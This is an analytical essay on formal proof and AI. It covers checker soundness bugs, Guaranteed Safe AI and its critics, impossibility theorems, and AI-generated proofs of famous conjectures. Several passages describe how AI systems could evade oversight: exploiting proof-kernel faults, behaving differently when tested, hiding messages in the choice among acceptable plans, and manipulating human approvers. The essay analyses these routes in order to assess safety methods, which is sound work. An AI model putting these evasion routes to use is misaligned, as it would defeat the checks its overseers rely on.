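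Suppose a prover works on 900 true statements, all of which it can prove, and 100 false ones. Suppose also that one in a billion attempts on a false statement happens to exploit a kernel fault. With 1,000 attempts on each false statement, the chance that the kernel accepts a proof of any of them is about 1 in 10,000. With a billion attempts on each, the chance for each statement is

1 − (1 − 10⁻⁹)^1,000,000,000 ≈ 63%.

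About 63 of the 963 accepted theorems, or 6.5%, would then be false. The kernel is the same in both cases, and only the amount of searching has changed.

Real systems can read the kernel's source code instead of searching at random, and one OpenAI agent used a single fault to prove a falsehood in two distinct ways. Brossard quotes Leonardo de Moura, Lean's creator, as writing, "This is going to keep happening." In December 2025, Rute (2025) had warned in a Lean discussion that an AI might exploit a soundness bug, though he noted that such tricks had been rare until then.

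A second checker helps because a searcher then needs either two faults or one that both checkers share. On the same assumptions, a second checker with independent faults would lower an attempt's chance of success from one in a billion to one in a billion billion. This is too optimistic, because a searcher with access to both checkers can look for a fault in each separately and combine the two in one proof, as the Collatz disproof did.

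The Collatz disproof was also easy to suspect, because a claimed solution to a famous problem attracts attention. A false proof that a file reader never leaks a password would look like thousands of valid ones, and perhaps nobody would examine it closely.

### Is ordinary software any safer?

An unverified program depends on the same compiler, runtime, operating system and hardware as a verified one, and nobody has proved that the program itself is correct. A fault in the proof checker's kernel can cause harm only if the program is also wrong. If 5% of programs are faulty and the kernel wrongly accepts one in a thousand of these, 0.005% of programs are both faulty and accepted, compared with 5% if programs are accepted without proofs.

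Checking a proof therefore cannot make a program less reliable, but it may lead people to take more risks. A company might stop testing, or run a stranger's code without reading it because it came with a proof. The kernel is then the main protection against a malicious author, and the 5% in the calculation no longer applies.

Kernel faults have not historically been the main reason verified work failed. In an older mailing-list discussion, Lawrence Paulson wrote that he had never seen a piece of work spoilt by a soundness bug in a prover, but had seen many spoilt by unrealistic models, incorrect axioms or proofs of irrelevant properties. The newsletter Computer Things similarly calls wrong assumptions arguably the most important source of bugs in code that has been proved correct. The known faults of 2026 don't contradict Paulson, because they were demonstrations and did not ruin any real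 project. But he was writing before AI systems could search for such bugs, and his experience is a poor guide to proofs from an untrusted prover.

### What to ask for

Someone who relies on a proof can learn a good deal by asking five questions:

1. What exactly does the theorem state, and on what definitions does it depend?
2. Which parts of the product does it cover?
3. What does it assume without proof?
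4. Which checkers accepted it, and in which versions?
5. How did the proved code become the program that actually runs?

Asking the second question about lean-zip would have shown that no theorem covered the archive reader. For the third, Lean has a single command that lists a theorem's axioms, the statements it assumes without proof. Three standard axioms are harmless, and any others need an explanation. In Rute's view, each added axiom makes a proof twice as hard to trust.

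The axiom list exposed a mock proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in 2026. Lean can accept the answer to a compiled calculation without checking each step, which is faster but adds the compiler to the trusted computing base. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* describes how the security company found a text operation whose compiled version disagreed with its logical definition, and used it to build the "proof". Lean showed its usual tick marks, but the list of axioms included an extra one for the compiled calculation. Lean's developers fixed the memory error behind the disagreement in about three hours and the rest in five days.

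How thoroughly a proof needs to be checked depends on who wrote it. The Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof* distinguishes honest proofs, which may contain mistakes, from malicious ones, which may be written to deceive the checker. It groups unreviewed AI-generated proofs with the malicious ones. For an honest proof, Lean's tick marks and the list of axioms are usually enough. For high-risk cases, such as proof competitions with large rewards, the reference recommends using the comparator tool with external checkers.

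The user first writes the theorem in a place the prover can't alter. Comparator, a tool for Lean, then checks that the submitted proof establishes the same statement and uses only permitted axioms. Users still have to trust the sandbox, which has a known weakness. Comparator's instructions on Reservoir, Lean's package site, include a safeguard against that weakness.

*Trustworthy Runtime Verification via Bisimulation (Extended Experience Report)* (2026) is unusually clear about what must still be trusted. It describes CopilotVerifier, a tool that checks automatically generated C code. The paper states that the tool's results depend on the C compiler Clang being correct, and that a bug in Clang could make them wrong. Users are left to make sure that a different compiler or different settings don't change what the program does. A customer who knows this can decide whether to compile with CompCert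 instead.

Few products come with such a statement, and many buyers would not know to ask for one. *Are Users More Willing to Use Formally Verified Password Managers?* (2025) found that users responded favourably to formal verification although they generally knew little about it. This suggests that the word "verified" could lead people to trust a product too much, but not that they take greater risks as a result. An earlier paper, *Exploring Usable Security to Improve the Impact of Formal Verification* (2021), called for research into users' misconceptions, but there still seems to be little such research.

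Experts sometimes encourage such misconceptions. The 2021 paper itself claims that formal verification can guarantee the absence of errors, and *The Industrialization of Noise* quotes Lean's home page as promising "absolute correctness". The password manager study proposes a label showing which parts of a product have been verified and to what extent. Such a label for lean-zip could have marked the compression code as proved and the archive reader as unproved.

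## Can proofs cover what an AI system does in the physical and social world?

Proofs can cover what an AI system does in the world only as far as a mathematical model predicts the effects of its actions. This is enough for hazards that engineers can bound with a safety margin, such as the temperature of a tank, but not for "harm" or "misinformation", because nobody can define these exactly or predict how people will use what an AI system tells them. Some researchers still regard proof as the only safe way to control very capable AI, while others claim that theorems of logic rule it out.

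### Guaranteed Safe AI

A shield can keep a cart or a car within limits. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) proposes a similar approach for much more ambitious systems, from household robots to an AI that designs ways to stabilise the climate. Its 17 authors include Yoshua Bengio, Stuart Russell and Clark Barrett, who helped design Reluplex. Dalrymple set up a programme called Safeguarded AI at the Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a British public funder, to put the approach into practice.

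In their definition, a guaranteed safe system comes with a quantitative guarantee that rests on three components. The world model is a mathematical description of how the system's actions affect its surroundings. The safety specification states which effects are acceptable. The verifier establishes that the system, or each of its outputs, meets the specification in the world model. The AI can be a black box because its proposals take effect only after the verifier approves them.

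The guarantee can be a proof that a violation never happens, a proved upper limit on the probability of one, or an estimate of that limit that becomes more reliable with more computing time. Dalrymple and colleagues grade each component by how much safety it would provide if it worked.

| Component | A low level | An intermediate level | The highest level |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model (0–5) | 1: a trained black-box simulator | 3: models of cause and effect that experts have fully audited | 5: no model, because the specification must hold in every possible world |
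| Safety specification (0–7) | 2: ordinary language that a black-box AI interprets | 4: logical formulas that use neural networks to recognise some human concepts | 7: everything people might want, in every situation |
| Verifier (0–10) | 1: ad hoc tests | 6: a search that would cover every input if it ran forever | 10: a proved limit, with a proof short enough for people to read |

Strong guarantees require a verifier at level 8 or above, but a good verifier can't make up for a poor world model. A level 10 proof about a level 1 simulator establishes only what happens in the simulator.

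Dalrymple and colleagues want more than tests because tests can miss rare failures, and because a capable system might recognise a test and behave differently in use. They compare AI with bridges, which they say became safer because of better theoretical understanding. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within a decade, while modern bridges fail at a rate below 0.4% per decade. This is a good argument for modelling but a weaker one for proof, because engineers achieved most of that improvement with calculations and safety margins.

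### The claim that there is no other way

A year earlier, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) made much stronger claims in *Provably safe systems*. They call proof the only path to guaranteed control of artificial general intelligence (AGI), meaning AI that can do most intellectual tasks at least as well as people. They also write that engineers can model physical, digital and even social systems precisely. In their plan, DNA synthesis machines, drones and AI chips would not operate without a proof of safety. Most of the powerful AI systems people used would be conventional programs with proofs attached, and neural networks would only help to discover them.

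Both men also signed the 2024 paper, which is more cautious. It allows for uncertainty, accepts neural networks, acknowledges there may be other ways to get a guarantee, and recommends testing alongside proof.

Tegmark and Omohundro use Gödel's completeness theorem to argue that provably safe systems are the only path to controllable AGI. According to the theorem, any statement that is true in every situation satisfying a set of axioms can be proved from those axioms. They infer that if a safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it, which a sufficiently powerful hostile AI may find.

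This inference fails because some situations satisfy the axioms but never occur. Suppose engineers know only that a tank warms by at most 6 degrees a minute, although it never warms by more than 4. They may be unable to prove that it stays below 50 degrees for five minutes, even though it could not reach 50 in that time. A missing proof may therefore mean only that the axioms are too weak. If the axioms are false, engineers may prove that a system is safe even though an attacker can break it.

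### Verified software on Mars

Andrew Dickson published a detailed critique of both papers in 2024. Nora Ammann, a co-author of the second paper, replies to him and other critics in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI*. Dickson mainly objects that people can prove things about systems of symbols, but not about the world. When the Perseverance rover landed on Mars in 2021, engineers had verified that its onboard software would run as designed. Nobody had proved that the landing would succeed, or even that a short circuit or a defective transistor wouldn't stop the software. If software faults made up a fifth of the risk, perfect software would have left the other four fifths.

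Ammann agrees that the guarantees are about a model and that no model matches the world perfectly. But she argues that a model can be accurate without being exact. She proposes over-approximation, which program verifiers use when they record only the range of a variable.

Suppose the water in a tank starts at 20 to 22 degrees and a heater warms it by 2 to 4 degrees a minute. The specification requires the water to stay below 50 degrees for five minutes. After five minutes, its temperature must be between 20 + 5 × 2 = 30 degrees and 22 + 5 × 4 = 42 degrees. This proves the water stays below 50 degrees the whole time, however the heating rate varies between 2 and 4 degrees a minute.

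This also answers part of Dickson's objection that engineers can't obtain complete data about the starting conditions. For the tank, they need only a thermometer accurate to within a degree. But as Dalrymple and colleagues concede in a footnote, even with a perfect theory of physics, engineers couldn't tell whether a molecule is poisonous without many facts about human cells. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest inferring such facts from data and treating the uncertainty cautiously, but they don't show that the resulting range would be narrow enough to be useful.

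Our understanding of physics may also change. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who doubts that a safety proof would still be relevant after the next revision of physics. This is hardly a worry for a heated tank, but it is more serious for an AI that could discover and use new physics. Ammann excludes such AIs from the systems the approach is meant to control.

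### When the model is wrong

If a fault raises the heating rate to 6 degrees a minute, the water could reach 22 + 5 × 6 = 52 degrees. The proof is still valid, but it no longer applies to this tank. A monitor that takes a reading every minute would detect a rise of 6 degrees after the first minute, but the model allows at most 4. The monitor could then switch off the heater while the water was at 28 degrees or below.

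The monitor may detect the fault late if it checks only whether each reading lies in the range predicted at the start. Water that began at 20 degrees would be at 26 after one minute, still within the predicted range of 22 to 26. The monitor would detect the fault only at the second reading, when the water was at 32 degrees instead of at most 30.

Monitoring works only if there is time to respond. If a fault could heat the water by 30 degrees in a minute, the temperature could pass 50 degrees between two readings. A late warning matters less in one of Ammann's examples, a table-tennis robot that Google DeepMind trained in simulation, because the worst likely result would be a lost point. The robot's designers modeled the bat's soft rubber with three extra springs and did not prove a limit on the error, but a monitor could detect when the ball departed from its predicted path.

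Dickson expects guarantees about the physical world to be approximate and to hold only for short periods. The tank's guarantee lasts just under seven minutes, since 22 + 7 × 4 = 50. Engineers can take a new reading and calculate again, but if the water has reached 42 degrees after five minutes, the new guarantee lasts less than two minutes. Ammann replies that short guarantees are enough if the system can always move to a safe state when nobody can renew them. Black-box Simplex works this way. Turning off the heater makes the tank safe, but a surgical robot can't safely stop in the middle of an operation.

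Some uncertainties have no firm limits, so the guarantee has to allow for the chance that the model is wrong. If that chance is at most ε in each step, Dalrymple and colleagues calculate that a specification proved for n steps will hold in reality with a probability of at least

(1 − ε)ⁿ.

With ε at one in a million and one step per second, this gives about 92% for a full day. But no proof can establish ε, so engineers have to estimate it from tests and experience. The guarantee therefore still depends on the kind of evidence it was supposed to improve on.

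### Which hazards have useful bounds?

A safe over-approximation always exists for rules about what a system must never do, because a system that does nothing obeys them all. But the bound is only worth using if it still lets the system do useful work.

DNA synthesis is the most disputed case. Tegmark and Omohundro want every synthesis machine to require a proof that the DNA is safe for humans. Two objections to this are convincing. Dickson argues that predicting whether a virus is dangerous would require simulating the entire human body at the molecular level. Hatfield-Dodds (2024), who maintains a widely used testing tool, says in the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that proving DNA safe for humans would take something like a thousand years of progress in microbiology.

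Dalrymple and colleagues also mention the narrower aim of building a machine that provably cannot make certain pathogens. For example, its software could refuse any order that shares a stretch of 50 letters with a genome on a list. Programmers could prove, without modelling the human body, that the software enforces this rule. However, the rule would miss a dangerous virus that nobody had listed, and a customer could evade it by ordering pieces of 49 letters and joining them. Refusing near matches and shorter stretches would catch more of these orders but also block more legitimate research.

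The critics' reading has some support in the proposal. In another example, Dalrymple and colleagues want an AI system to reject any sequence that people could use to produce pathogens, toxic chemicals or other harmful substances, which is far harder than checking orders against a list.

Ammann suggests a rule between these two. A virus has to get into a human cell to infect someone, so software could check whether any of the virus's proteins, paired with any protein on the surface of human cells, would let it in. If no pair would, the virus can't infect people. The rule would also exclude some useful gene therapies, which makes it an over-approximation.

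With 30 viral proteins and 3,000 surface proteins, a computer would have only 90,000 pairs to check, but proving that entry is impossible for each pair is difficult. Some viruses, such as herpes simplex, also need several of their proteins to act together, so checking one pair at a time might miss them. And a gene that makes bacteria produce a toxin could hurt people without any virus. Ammann offers the idea as an illustration and acknowledges that it is beyond current capabilities.

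| Hazard | Is there an exact specification? | What must the model predict? | Is there a useful bound? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Login without valid credentials | Yes | How the computer behaves | Yes, if the hardware works as specified |
| Overheated tank | Yes | The range of heating rates | Yes, with a monitor |
| Synthesis of a listed pathogen | Yes | How the machine behaves | Yes, but only for the list |
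| Any virus that can infect people | Possibly, as entry into a human cell | How proteins interact | Not yet |
| Harmful advice | No | What people do with the advice | No |
| Misinformation | No | What people come to believe | No |

Researchers have proposed formal definitions of harm, but Dalrymple and colleagues admit that the word is vague and that people disagree about borderline cases. Misinformation is no easier to define, because even a true statement can mislead. For example, an accurate report of a plane crash might convince somebody that flying is more dangerous than driving. Ammann agrees with the critics on this point. She considers the approach unsuitable for chatbots and better suited to well-understood, non-chaotic fields, such as electricity grids and supply chains.

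### Bounds on what people do

Even a power grid depends on people, though engineers can often predict a crowd better than an individual. Suppose each of a million households has a 1% chance of boiling a kettle in a given minute, independently of the others. The number of kettles in use will almost certainly be between 9,500 and 10,500. This calculation is reliable only if the households act independently. If many of them are watching the same football match, they may all put the kettle on at half-time, and demand could be several times higher.

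Dalrymple and colleagues propose modelling an individual's behaviour as a set of possibilities and requiring the specification to hold for all of them. Suppose a pedestrian is walking one metre from a car's path and could move at 2 m/s in any direction. She could be in front of the car within half a second. A car that brakes at 5 m/s² can stop in that time only if it is travelling at 2.5 m/s (9 km/h) or less, even with no delay before braking. A car proved safe for everything a pedestrian might do would therefore have to drive this slowly whenever it passed one this close.

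Engineers could instead assume that pedestrians don't step into the road without looking. The car could then drive at a normal speed, but the proof would not cover a child running after a ball. Covering more pedestrian behaviours makes the guarantee stronger but the car slower, so choosing which ones to cover is partly a decision about acceptable risk. Because the assumption is explicit, regulators and the public can at least debate it.

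Tegmark and Omohundro also want secure hardware to enforce rules about who may authorise dangerous actions. A proof might establish that a DNA machine never runs without the digital signatures of two licensed scientists, but not that nobody had deceived or bribed them. Tegmark and Omohundro recognise that a powerful AI could manipulate people through persuasion, bribery or blackmail, which is one reason they want to limit the power of small groups. Requiring more signatures makes an attack harder, but somebody still has to judge whether the action is a good idea.

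### Has the problem only moved?

Hatfield-Dodds argues that Guaranteed Safe AI only moves the problem, because its supporters still have to convince him that the world model matches reality closely enough. He would prefer them to spend their time on threat modelling, which means listing what could go wrong and asking why it would or wouldn't be a problem. He considers formal verification a valuable part of a wider set of methods, but thinks its advocates claim too much for it.

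Ammann replies that every approach to AI safety relies on beliefs about the world, and that a world model makes these beliefs explicit. This is true, but explicit beliefs can still be false. A more practical advantage is that the model may be far simpler than the AI. Dalrymple and colleagues point out that the rules of chess are much less complex than a program that plays well. Engineers can also reuse one model of a power grid to check thousands of plans, including plans from AI systems that don't exist yet. Relying on a world model is therefore worthwhile when a relatively simple model covers many decisions, but achieves little if each new decision needs a new model of society.

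A capable AI may also make errors in the model more dangerous. If it searches for the best plan that passes the check, it may find one that looks best only because the model leaves out a drawback or a danger. Dalrymple and colleagues describe the same problem with measurable proxies for harm, which can match people's judgement in normal situations but fail once a system optimises for them.

Critics have also suggested that an AI could hide harmful information in a plan that passes every check. Ammann proposes requiring a proof that the plan is the only one that meets the requirements. The AI can then either give that plan or decline, which conveys at most one bit of information. But most practical tasks have many acceptable plans. If 100 generators each have ten acceptable settings, there are 10¹⁰⁰ acceptable plans, and the choice between them can carry about 332 bits, enough for a message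 of roughly 40 characters. Engineers could make the plan unique by requiring the cheapest one and adding a rule for breaking ties, but proving that a plan is the cheapest is usually harder than proving that it is safe.

Dickson also asks how anyone can know that the machine in front of them is the one the proof describes. It might have a manufacturing defect or a secret back door. Ammann proposes tamper-resistant hardware and cryptographic methods that tie a proof to a particular system. These could stop somebody from passing off one device as another, but people would still have to trust the hardware and whoever inspected it.

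### Can verified systems compete with learned ones?

Hatfield-Dodds also doubts that explicit, verified software can match machine learning at the tasks machine learning does best. If it can't, companies will keep using learned systems for those tasks, and someone will still have to deal with the risks. He doesn't think restricting AI to tools that only answer questions would help much either. A user could turn such a tool into an agent by writing a simple program that repeatedly queries it for the best next action and carries that action out.

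Tegmark and Omohundro reply to the first point that neural networks are powerful because they learn well, not because of how they run. Once a network has learned a good algorithm, they expect that engineers can extract it as ordinary code without losing performance. This might work for a compact algorithm such as a sorting method. It is much less plausible for recognising a pedestrian, where there may be no short algorithm to find. They also give no example of a competitive system that anyone has converted this way.

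The objection is weaker against the design of Dalrymple and colleagues, who let a neural network propose actions and verify only those actions. Their system can use the best available model, so its only competitive disadvantages are the delay and the good actions that the verifier rejects. Because the design doesn't require verifying the network itself, Hatfield-Dodds's remark that even a network with a few billion parameters is far too large to verify doesn't refute it.

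### Will help from AI come too late?

Building world models by hand is slow, so both proposals depend on AI to speed it up. Dickson accepts that AI will help people write proofs, but sees little evidence that it will help much with modelling and specification. He argues that if such help requires an AI more capable than any human expert, it will arrive after the dangers it was meant to prevent. Tegmark and Omohundro share part of this worry, writing that an AI may need to be at least an AGI before it can turn its own knowledge into code, and that by then it may be too late.

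Ammann expects AI to help with models much as it already helps with programming, by suggesting formulas, proposing changes and producing surprising cases for people to examine. Experts would still write and audit the models, so that a hostile or mistaken AI could not change the assumptions without anyone noticing. As evidence of progress, she notes that automated provers' success rate on miniF2F, a set of mathematical problems, had risen from 26% to 63% in a year.

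Results since then support both sides. LLMs now write most of the proofs in several programming benchmarks, as Ammann hoped. But on AuXSpec's problems, even Claude Opus 5 was much worse at writing specifications than programs. Physical models may be even harder to get right, because the only way to check them is to measure the world. An LLM can propose a heating rate for a tank in seconds, but somebody has to heat the tank to check it.

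### Do impossibility theorems rule it out?

Rice's theorem shows that no tool can decide, for every program, whether it has a given nontrivial behavioral property. Two recent papers apply similar reasoning to AGI. In *Limitations on Safe, Trusted, Artificial General Intelligence*, Panigrahy and Sharan (2025) prove that no system can be safe, trusted and an AGI at once. They call a system safe if it never makes a false claim, though it may answer "don't know", and trusted if people assume it is safe. To count as an AGI, it must be able to solve every problem for which a human has a provably correct solution.

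The simplest example uses a system A that predicts whether programs always stop. The following program runs A on its own code and does the opposite of what A predicts.

```
def g():
    if A(g) == "always stops":
        while True:
            pass
    return 0
```

If A answered "always stops", g would run forever and the answer would be false. If A is safe, it can't give that answer, so g returns 0 and stops. Anyone who trusts A can therefore conclude that g always stops, but A can never give that answer.

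The proof is valid but has little practical importance. Like the hallucination theorem, it uses a problem built to contradict one particular system. A different verifier could approve g, and A could still prove that if A is safe, then g stops. The definition of AGI is also so strict that one such failure disqualifies a system that outperforms people at everything else. Panigrahy and Sharan acknowledge that looser definitions avoid the conflict and may still be useful in practice.

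Gumbau Mezquita (2026), in *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic*, considers systems that rewrite themselves. Whether a program will still be safe after its next change is a question about its behaviour, so under certain conditions on how programs change, Rice's theorem implies that no algorithm can answer it for every program. He concludes that only a system whose behaviour has stopped changing can have a lasting certificate.

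That conclusion doesn't follow from the theorem. Suppose version n of a program takes a whole number x, zero or greater, and returns x + n, using integers of unlimited size. Each version behaves differently, but it is easy to prove that none will return a negative number. The theorem rules out a method that works for all self-changing programs, but it still allows proofs about particular ones. If a shield limits a robot's speed, the proof of that limit holds however often the controller rewrites itself, as long as the controller can't change the shield.

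Gumbau Mezquita also argues that any checker that examines only finitely many inputs can miss a violation on the others. This is a sound argument against relying on tests, but a verifier that analyzes the program's code can cover infinitely many inputs with a finite proof. Dafny, for example, proves the absolute-value function correct for all integers.

He similarly objects to having one AGI supervise another, because the supervisor would be just as hard to verify. A proof checker avoids this problem because it can be far simpler than the system that writes the proofs. Tegmark and Omohundro cite a 300-line Python checker for the proof language Metamath.

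The main reply to these theorems is that engineers can design systems to be verifiable and reject any program without a proof, so they don't have to decide whether every possible program is safe. Gumbau Mezquita accepts that shields and compulsory proofs avoid his theorems, but regards them as sacrifices. The checker will reject some safe actions because nobody can find a short enough proof, and the system must wait for approval after every change. The operator of a power grid might well accept that delay. A company racing to build the most capable AI would be tempted to skip the proofs, since a rival that skipped them could improve its system faster.

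## Is proof worth its cost as models become more reliable?

Proof is still worth the effort for results that many people build on and for software that attackers will search for faults. For most everyday software, good tests are a better use of that effort. Models that make fewer errors weaken the case for proof, but they also reduce the effort of writing proofs and produce far more work than people can read. Mathematics has gone through these changes faster than any other field.

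### Gold medals without Lean

In July 2024, Google DeepMind's AlphaProof and a companion system for geometry reached the silver-medal standard at the International Mathematical Olympiad, a competition for school students. People translated the problems into Lean by hand. A neural network then proposed proof steps, and Lean rejected the invalid ones. The network had learned by attempting millions of formal problems and repeating whatever led to accepted proofs.

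A year later, general models from Google and OpenAI reached the gold standard in ordinary English.

| System | Proofs written in | Time | Points out of 42 |
|---|---|---|---|
| AlphaProof and AlphaGeometry 2, 2024 | Lean and a language for geometry | Up to three days for one problem | 28 |
| Gemini Deep Think, 2025 | English | Contest time | 35 |
| OpenAI's experimental model, 2025 | English | Contest time | 35 |
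| ByteDance's Seed-Prover, 2025 | Lean and a language for geometry | Three days | 30 |

Seed-Prover completed a fifth problem after the deadline, so the Lean systems were not far behind. But the general models were faster and needed no translator, which is the best evidence for the objection that better models will make formal checking unnecessary.

However, the contest tests whether a system can find a proof. Experts checked the solutions, and they had only a handful to mark and already knew the answers. By contrast, when OpenAI presented a model's attempts at ten research-level problems in *Our First Proof submissions* (2026), it acknowledged that their correctness was hard to establish without expert review.

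### Does the bitter lesson apply to checkers?

In his 2019 essay *The Bitter Lesson*, the computer scientist Rich Sutton argued that AI researchers repeatedly build human knowledge into their systems, make quick progress, and then lose to general methods that use more computing power. His examples include chess, Go and speech recognition. A sceptic of formal proof could add the Olympiad, where models without any built-in logic overtook one that had to work in Lean.

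The usual reply is that a checker outside the model doesn't constrain how the model learns. DeepMind's AlphaZero, for example, learned Go without any human games or strategies, but it still needed the rules to determine who had won. A proof checker similarly determines whether a proof is valid. It can give the model as much reliable feedback as the developers have the computing power to generate, and a general method needs that feedback. Metz describes how AI systems learn to write better Lean through this kind of trial and error.

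This reply is convincing for a checker that sees only finished work, but weaker for designs that restrict the model while it works. CaMeL's planner has to fix its plan before it sees any data, however good it is at using data. A world model written by hand may also leave out the best plan because its designers never thought of it. Making a model do all its reasoning in Lean is another restriction, and the 2025 results suggest that it hurt performance. In 2026, OpenAI let a model find proofs however it could and had it formalise them afterwards.

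### The price of a formal proof

Writing formal proofs by hand is slow. In Spektrum's *Beweisprüfer und KI*, the mathematician Floris van Doorn estimates that a one-page textbook proof takes days or weeks to formalize, even if the proof assistant already contains all the necessary concepts.

AI has changed this. In September 2026, OpenAI announced a solution to the Navier-Stokes problem, which asks whether the equations of fluid motion always have well-behaved solutions. According to Mint's *Why are mathematicians concerned about OpenAI’s AI solving problems*, the company said its model took about 88 hours to find the solution and another 17 to formalise and verify it. Formalisation and verification therefore took only about 16% of the total time. A month earlier, OpenAI's *Ten advances in mathematics and theoretical computer science* had presented a Lean proof for each of its ten results.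 It put the cost of finding them at roughly $2,000 in tokens, which Willison (2026) interprets as the cost per result.

Formalising a proof is much harder when the results it relies on have not been formalised. An OpenAI model's solution to the Erdős unit distance problem, a question in geometry, was 18 pages long. The Lean version has 1.2 million lines, mainly because it relies on a deep theorem that nobody had formalised, according to Epoch AI. Mathematicians call the ratio of the formal length to the ordinary length the de Bruijn factor. At 40 lines to a page, the factor for this proof is about 1,700. Computational Complexity (2026), a blog about theoretical computer science, suggests that the de Bruijn factor may explain why the field has so few formal proofs.

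A Lean proof also establishes only its formal statement. Anders Hansen of the University of Cambridge and his team found that the Lean proof for Navier-Stokes does not correspond to the written paper, according to Hindustan Times' *OpenAI’s approach to mathematics does not add up*. Hansen thinks the Lean code contains a solution, and OpenAI says its models may have found two. If so, the result holds, but Lean never checked the argument in the paper.

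The gap may be more serious for Yang-Mills theory, which underlies much of particle physics. In October, OpenAI claimed a proof that the theory exists mathematically, which is part of another famous open problem. After a committee of physicists released the Lean code, Peter Woit argued in *The Yang-Mills Publicity Stunt* that it proves only a weak form of existence. The official problem description, which he quotes, excludes this form unless further properties are also proved. Woit is a fierce critic of the project, but his objection is about the wording of the theorem, so anyone who knows the field can check it. A more reliable model would not settle this dispute, because both sides can accept that the proof is correct.

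### 722 manuscripts at once

On 6 October 2026, OpenAI published 722 manuscripts written by an unreleased model, covering 372 groups of related problems. About 42% of the main results came with a Lean proof, according to Infobae's *OpenAI publica 700 trabajos matemáticos de IA entre errores y cuestionamientos* (2026).

OpenAI withdrew three of its 722 manuscripts within a day of releasing them because of a single sign error. Retraction Watch's *OpenAI withdraws three preprints a day after releasing 722 manuscripts* (2026) reports that the error invalidated an argument in one manuscript and a construction that the other two relied on. OpenAI also revised 14 others. An attempt to formalize the faulty argument in Lean would have failed at the wrong sign.

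Seventeen corrections among 722 manuscripts is not many, but it includes only the faults found in the first days. The mathematician Andrew Sutherland expects most of the results to be correct or repairable, but he expects some of the proofs to contain errors, possibly serious ones. He wants OpenAI to publish the problems its model failed to solve, which the company says number in the thousands.

The number of failures matters because it affects how far to trust the successes. Suppose a model attempts 3,000 problems and solves 300. On 2% of the other 2,700, it produces a wrong proof that looks convincing. It therefore reports 354 results, of which 54, or 15%, are wrong. If it had attempted only 600 problems and solved the same 300, it would have reported six wrong results, or 2% of the total, even though the rate of convincing wrong proofs on unsolved problems was the same. As models improve,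 people will give them harder problems, so the share of wrong results may not fall as quickly as one would expect. The number of failed attempts does not affect how far to trust a result with a sound formal proof.

Human checking also takes time that few experts have. Kevin Buzzard, a number theorist at Imperial College London, looked at 30 of the manuscripts. He found seven relevant, and only one had a Lean proof, according to Infobae's *Un error obliga a OpenAI a retirar tres estudios matemáticos* (2026). Alex Townsend of Cornell University thinks OpenAI should have announced the verified manuscripts first. This is sensible, because experts could then have concentrated on what the results mean instead of looking for sign errors.

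Formal proof doesn't make a paper worth reading, though. Roland Bauerschmidt of New York University called some of the texts AI slop, and a colleague of the mathematician Melissa Lee could not understand the manuscript on one of his favourite problems.

### A library for later proofs

A month later, the company Axiom announced that its AI agents had formalised the Stacks Project, a reference work on algebraic geometry that mathematicians have been writing since 2005. The agents turned about 7,654 pages into roughly 16 million lines of Lean, according to Mehta in *Axiom Math wants to keep AI slop out of mathematics*. That is about 2,100 lines per page, compared with 67,000 for the unit distance proof. The Stacks Project probably needed fewer lines per page largely because each result in it can build on earlier ones.

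Reuse is also the main economic argument for the project. If a missing theorem takes a million lines to prove, it is wasteful for every team that needs the theorem to rewrite the proof. Terence Tao makes the general point that "the more formalized proofs you have, the more formalized proofs you can make."

But the figures come from Axiom. A library is also useful only if other people can work with its definitions. A slightly wrong definition can affect every theorem that uses it, so specialists have to compare the important definitions with the original text.

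### The Riemann hypothesis

The Riemann hypothesis, which dates from 1859, states that a function encoding the distribution of prime numbers is zero only at the negative even integers and at complex numbers whose real part is ½. On 20 November 2026, Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at Anthropic, announced a proof developed with Claude. He published a four-page note and 17,374,215 lines of Lean in 175,187 files, according to HeadTopics' *リーマン予想の証明をClaudeと共同で完成、Leanで検証完了* (2026). Reading the Lean code at one line a second for eight hours a day would take about 603 days.

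The Lean and Mathlib communities' *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) certified the proof one day later. Mathlib is Lean's main library of mathematics. The statement gives four reasons for confidence:

1. The formal statement of the hypothesis is correct. It was already part of Mathlib, and experts had examined it carefully.
2. Dozens of people compiled the code and obtained the same exported proof.
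3. Two independent tools confirmed that the theorem in Alpöge's code is exactly the one in Mathlib.
4. Several checkers accepted the exported proof, including Lean's kernel and programs by other developers in different languages.

The first of these reasons is especially strong because *Formalizing zeta and L-functions in Lean* (Loeffler and Stoll, 2025) described a formal statement 20 months before anyone had a proof, so nobody could have adjusted it to suit Alpöge's argument. Two of the checkers, con-leche and con-ron, come with a formal proof that they cannot accept a false theorem, as long as set theory is consistent. This was a useful precaution after the kernel faults found in the summer.

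Sutherland ran several of these checks himself. The independent checker nanoda took about 28 minutes, and con-leche took about three. He also found that the proof uses only Lean's three standard axioms.

A rival proof shows how much slower the traditional method is. Alessandro Maria Masullo wrote a 900-page draft without AI and shared it with other mathematicians months before Alpöge's announcement. They were still working through it in late November, according to Understanding AI's *An Anthropic mathematician just solved math’s most famous problem*. Even if Masullo were a more reliable author, they would have had to check the draft, because they could not have known in advance that he was right.

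By early December, the proof had become much shorter but was still hard to understand. On 25 November, Luke Sernau and colleagues at Anthropic used Claude to produce a version with 76,000 lines and a more readable one with about 300,000. Both prove the same main theorems. Root.cz's *Důkaz Riemannovy hypotézy zkrácen o 99,6 %* describes two accounts in ordinary mathematical language, of 1,687 and 1,155 pages. AI did much of the writing, and nobody had yet fully and independently reviewed either account. Michael Rubinstein of the University of Waterloo had summarised the basic argument in 15 steps.

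The Clay Mathematics Institute had not decided whether to award its $1 million prize for solving the Riemann hypothesis. Its president, Martin Bridson, said the rules came from a "pre-AI era", according to International Business Times' *Claude-Assisted Proof of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026).

Axiom has announced an extension to a wider family of functions. The proof assumes three published theorems without proving them in Lean, and somebody still has to confirm that the formal versions match the originals. This makes its guarantee weaker than that of Alpöge's proof, although Lean accepts both.

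### What is an unreadable proof good for?

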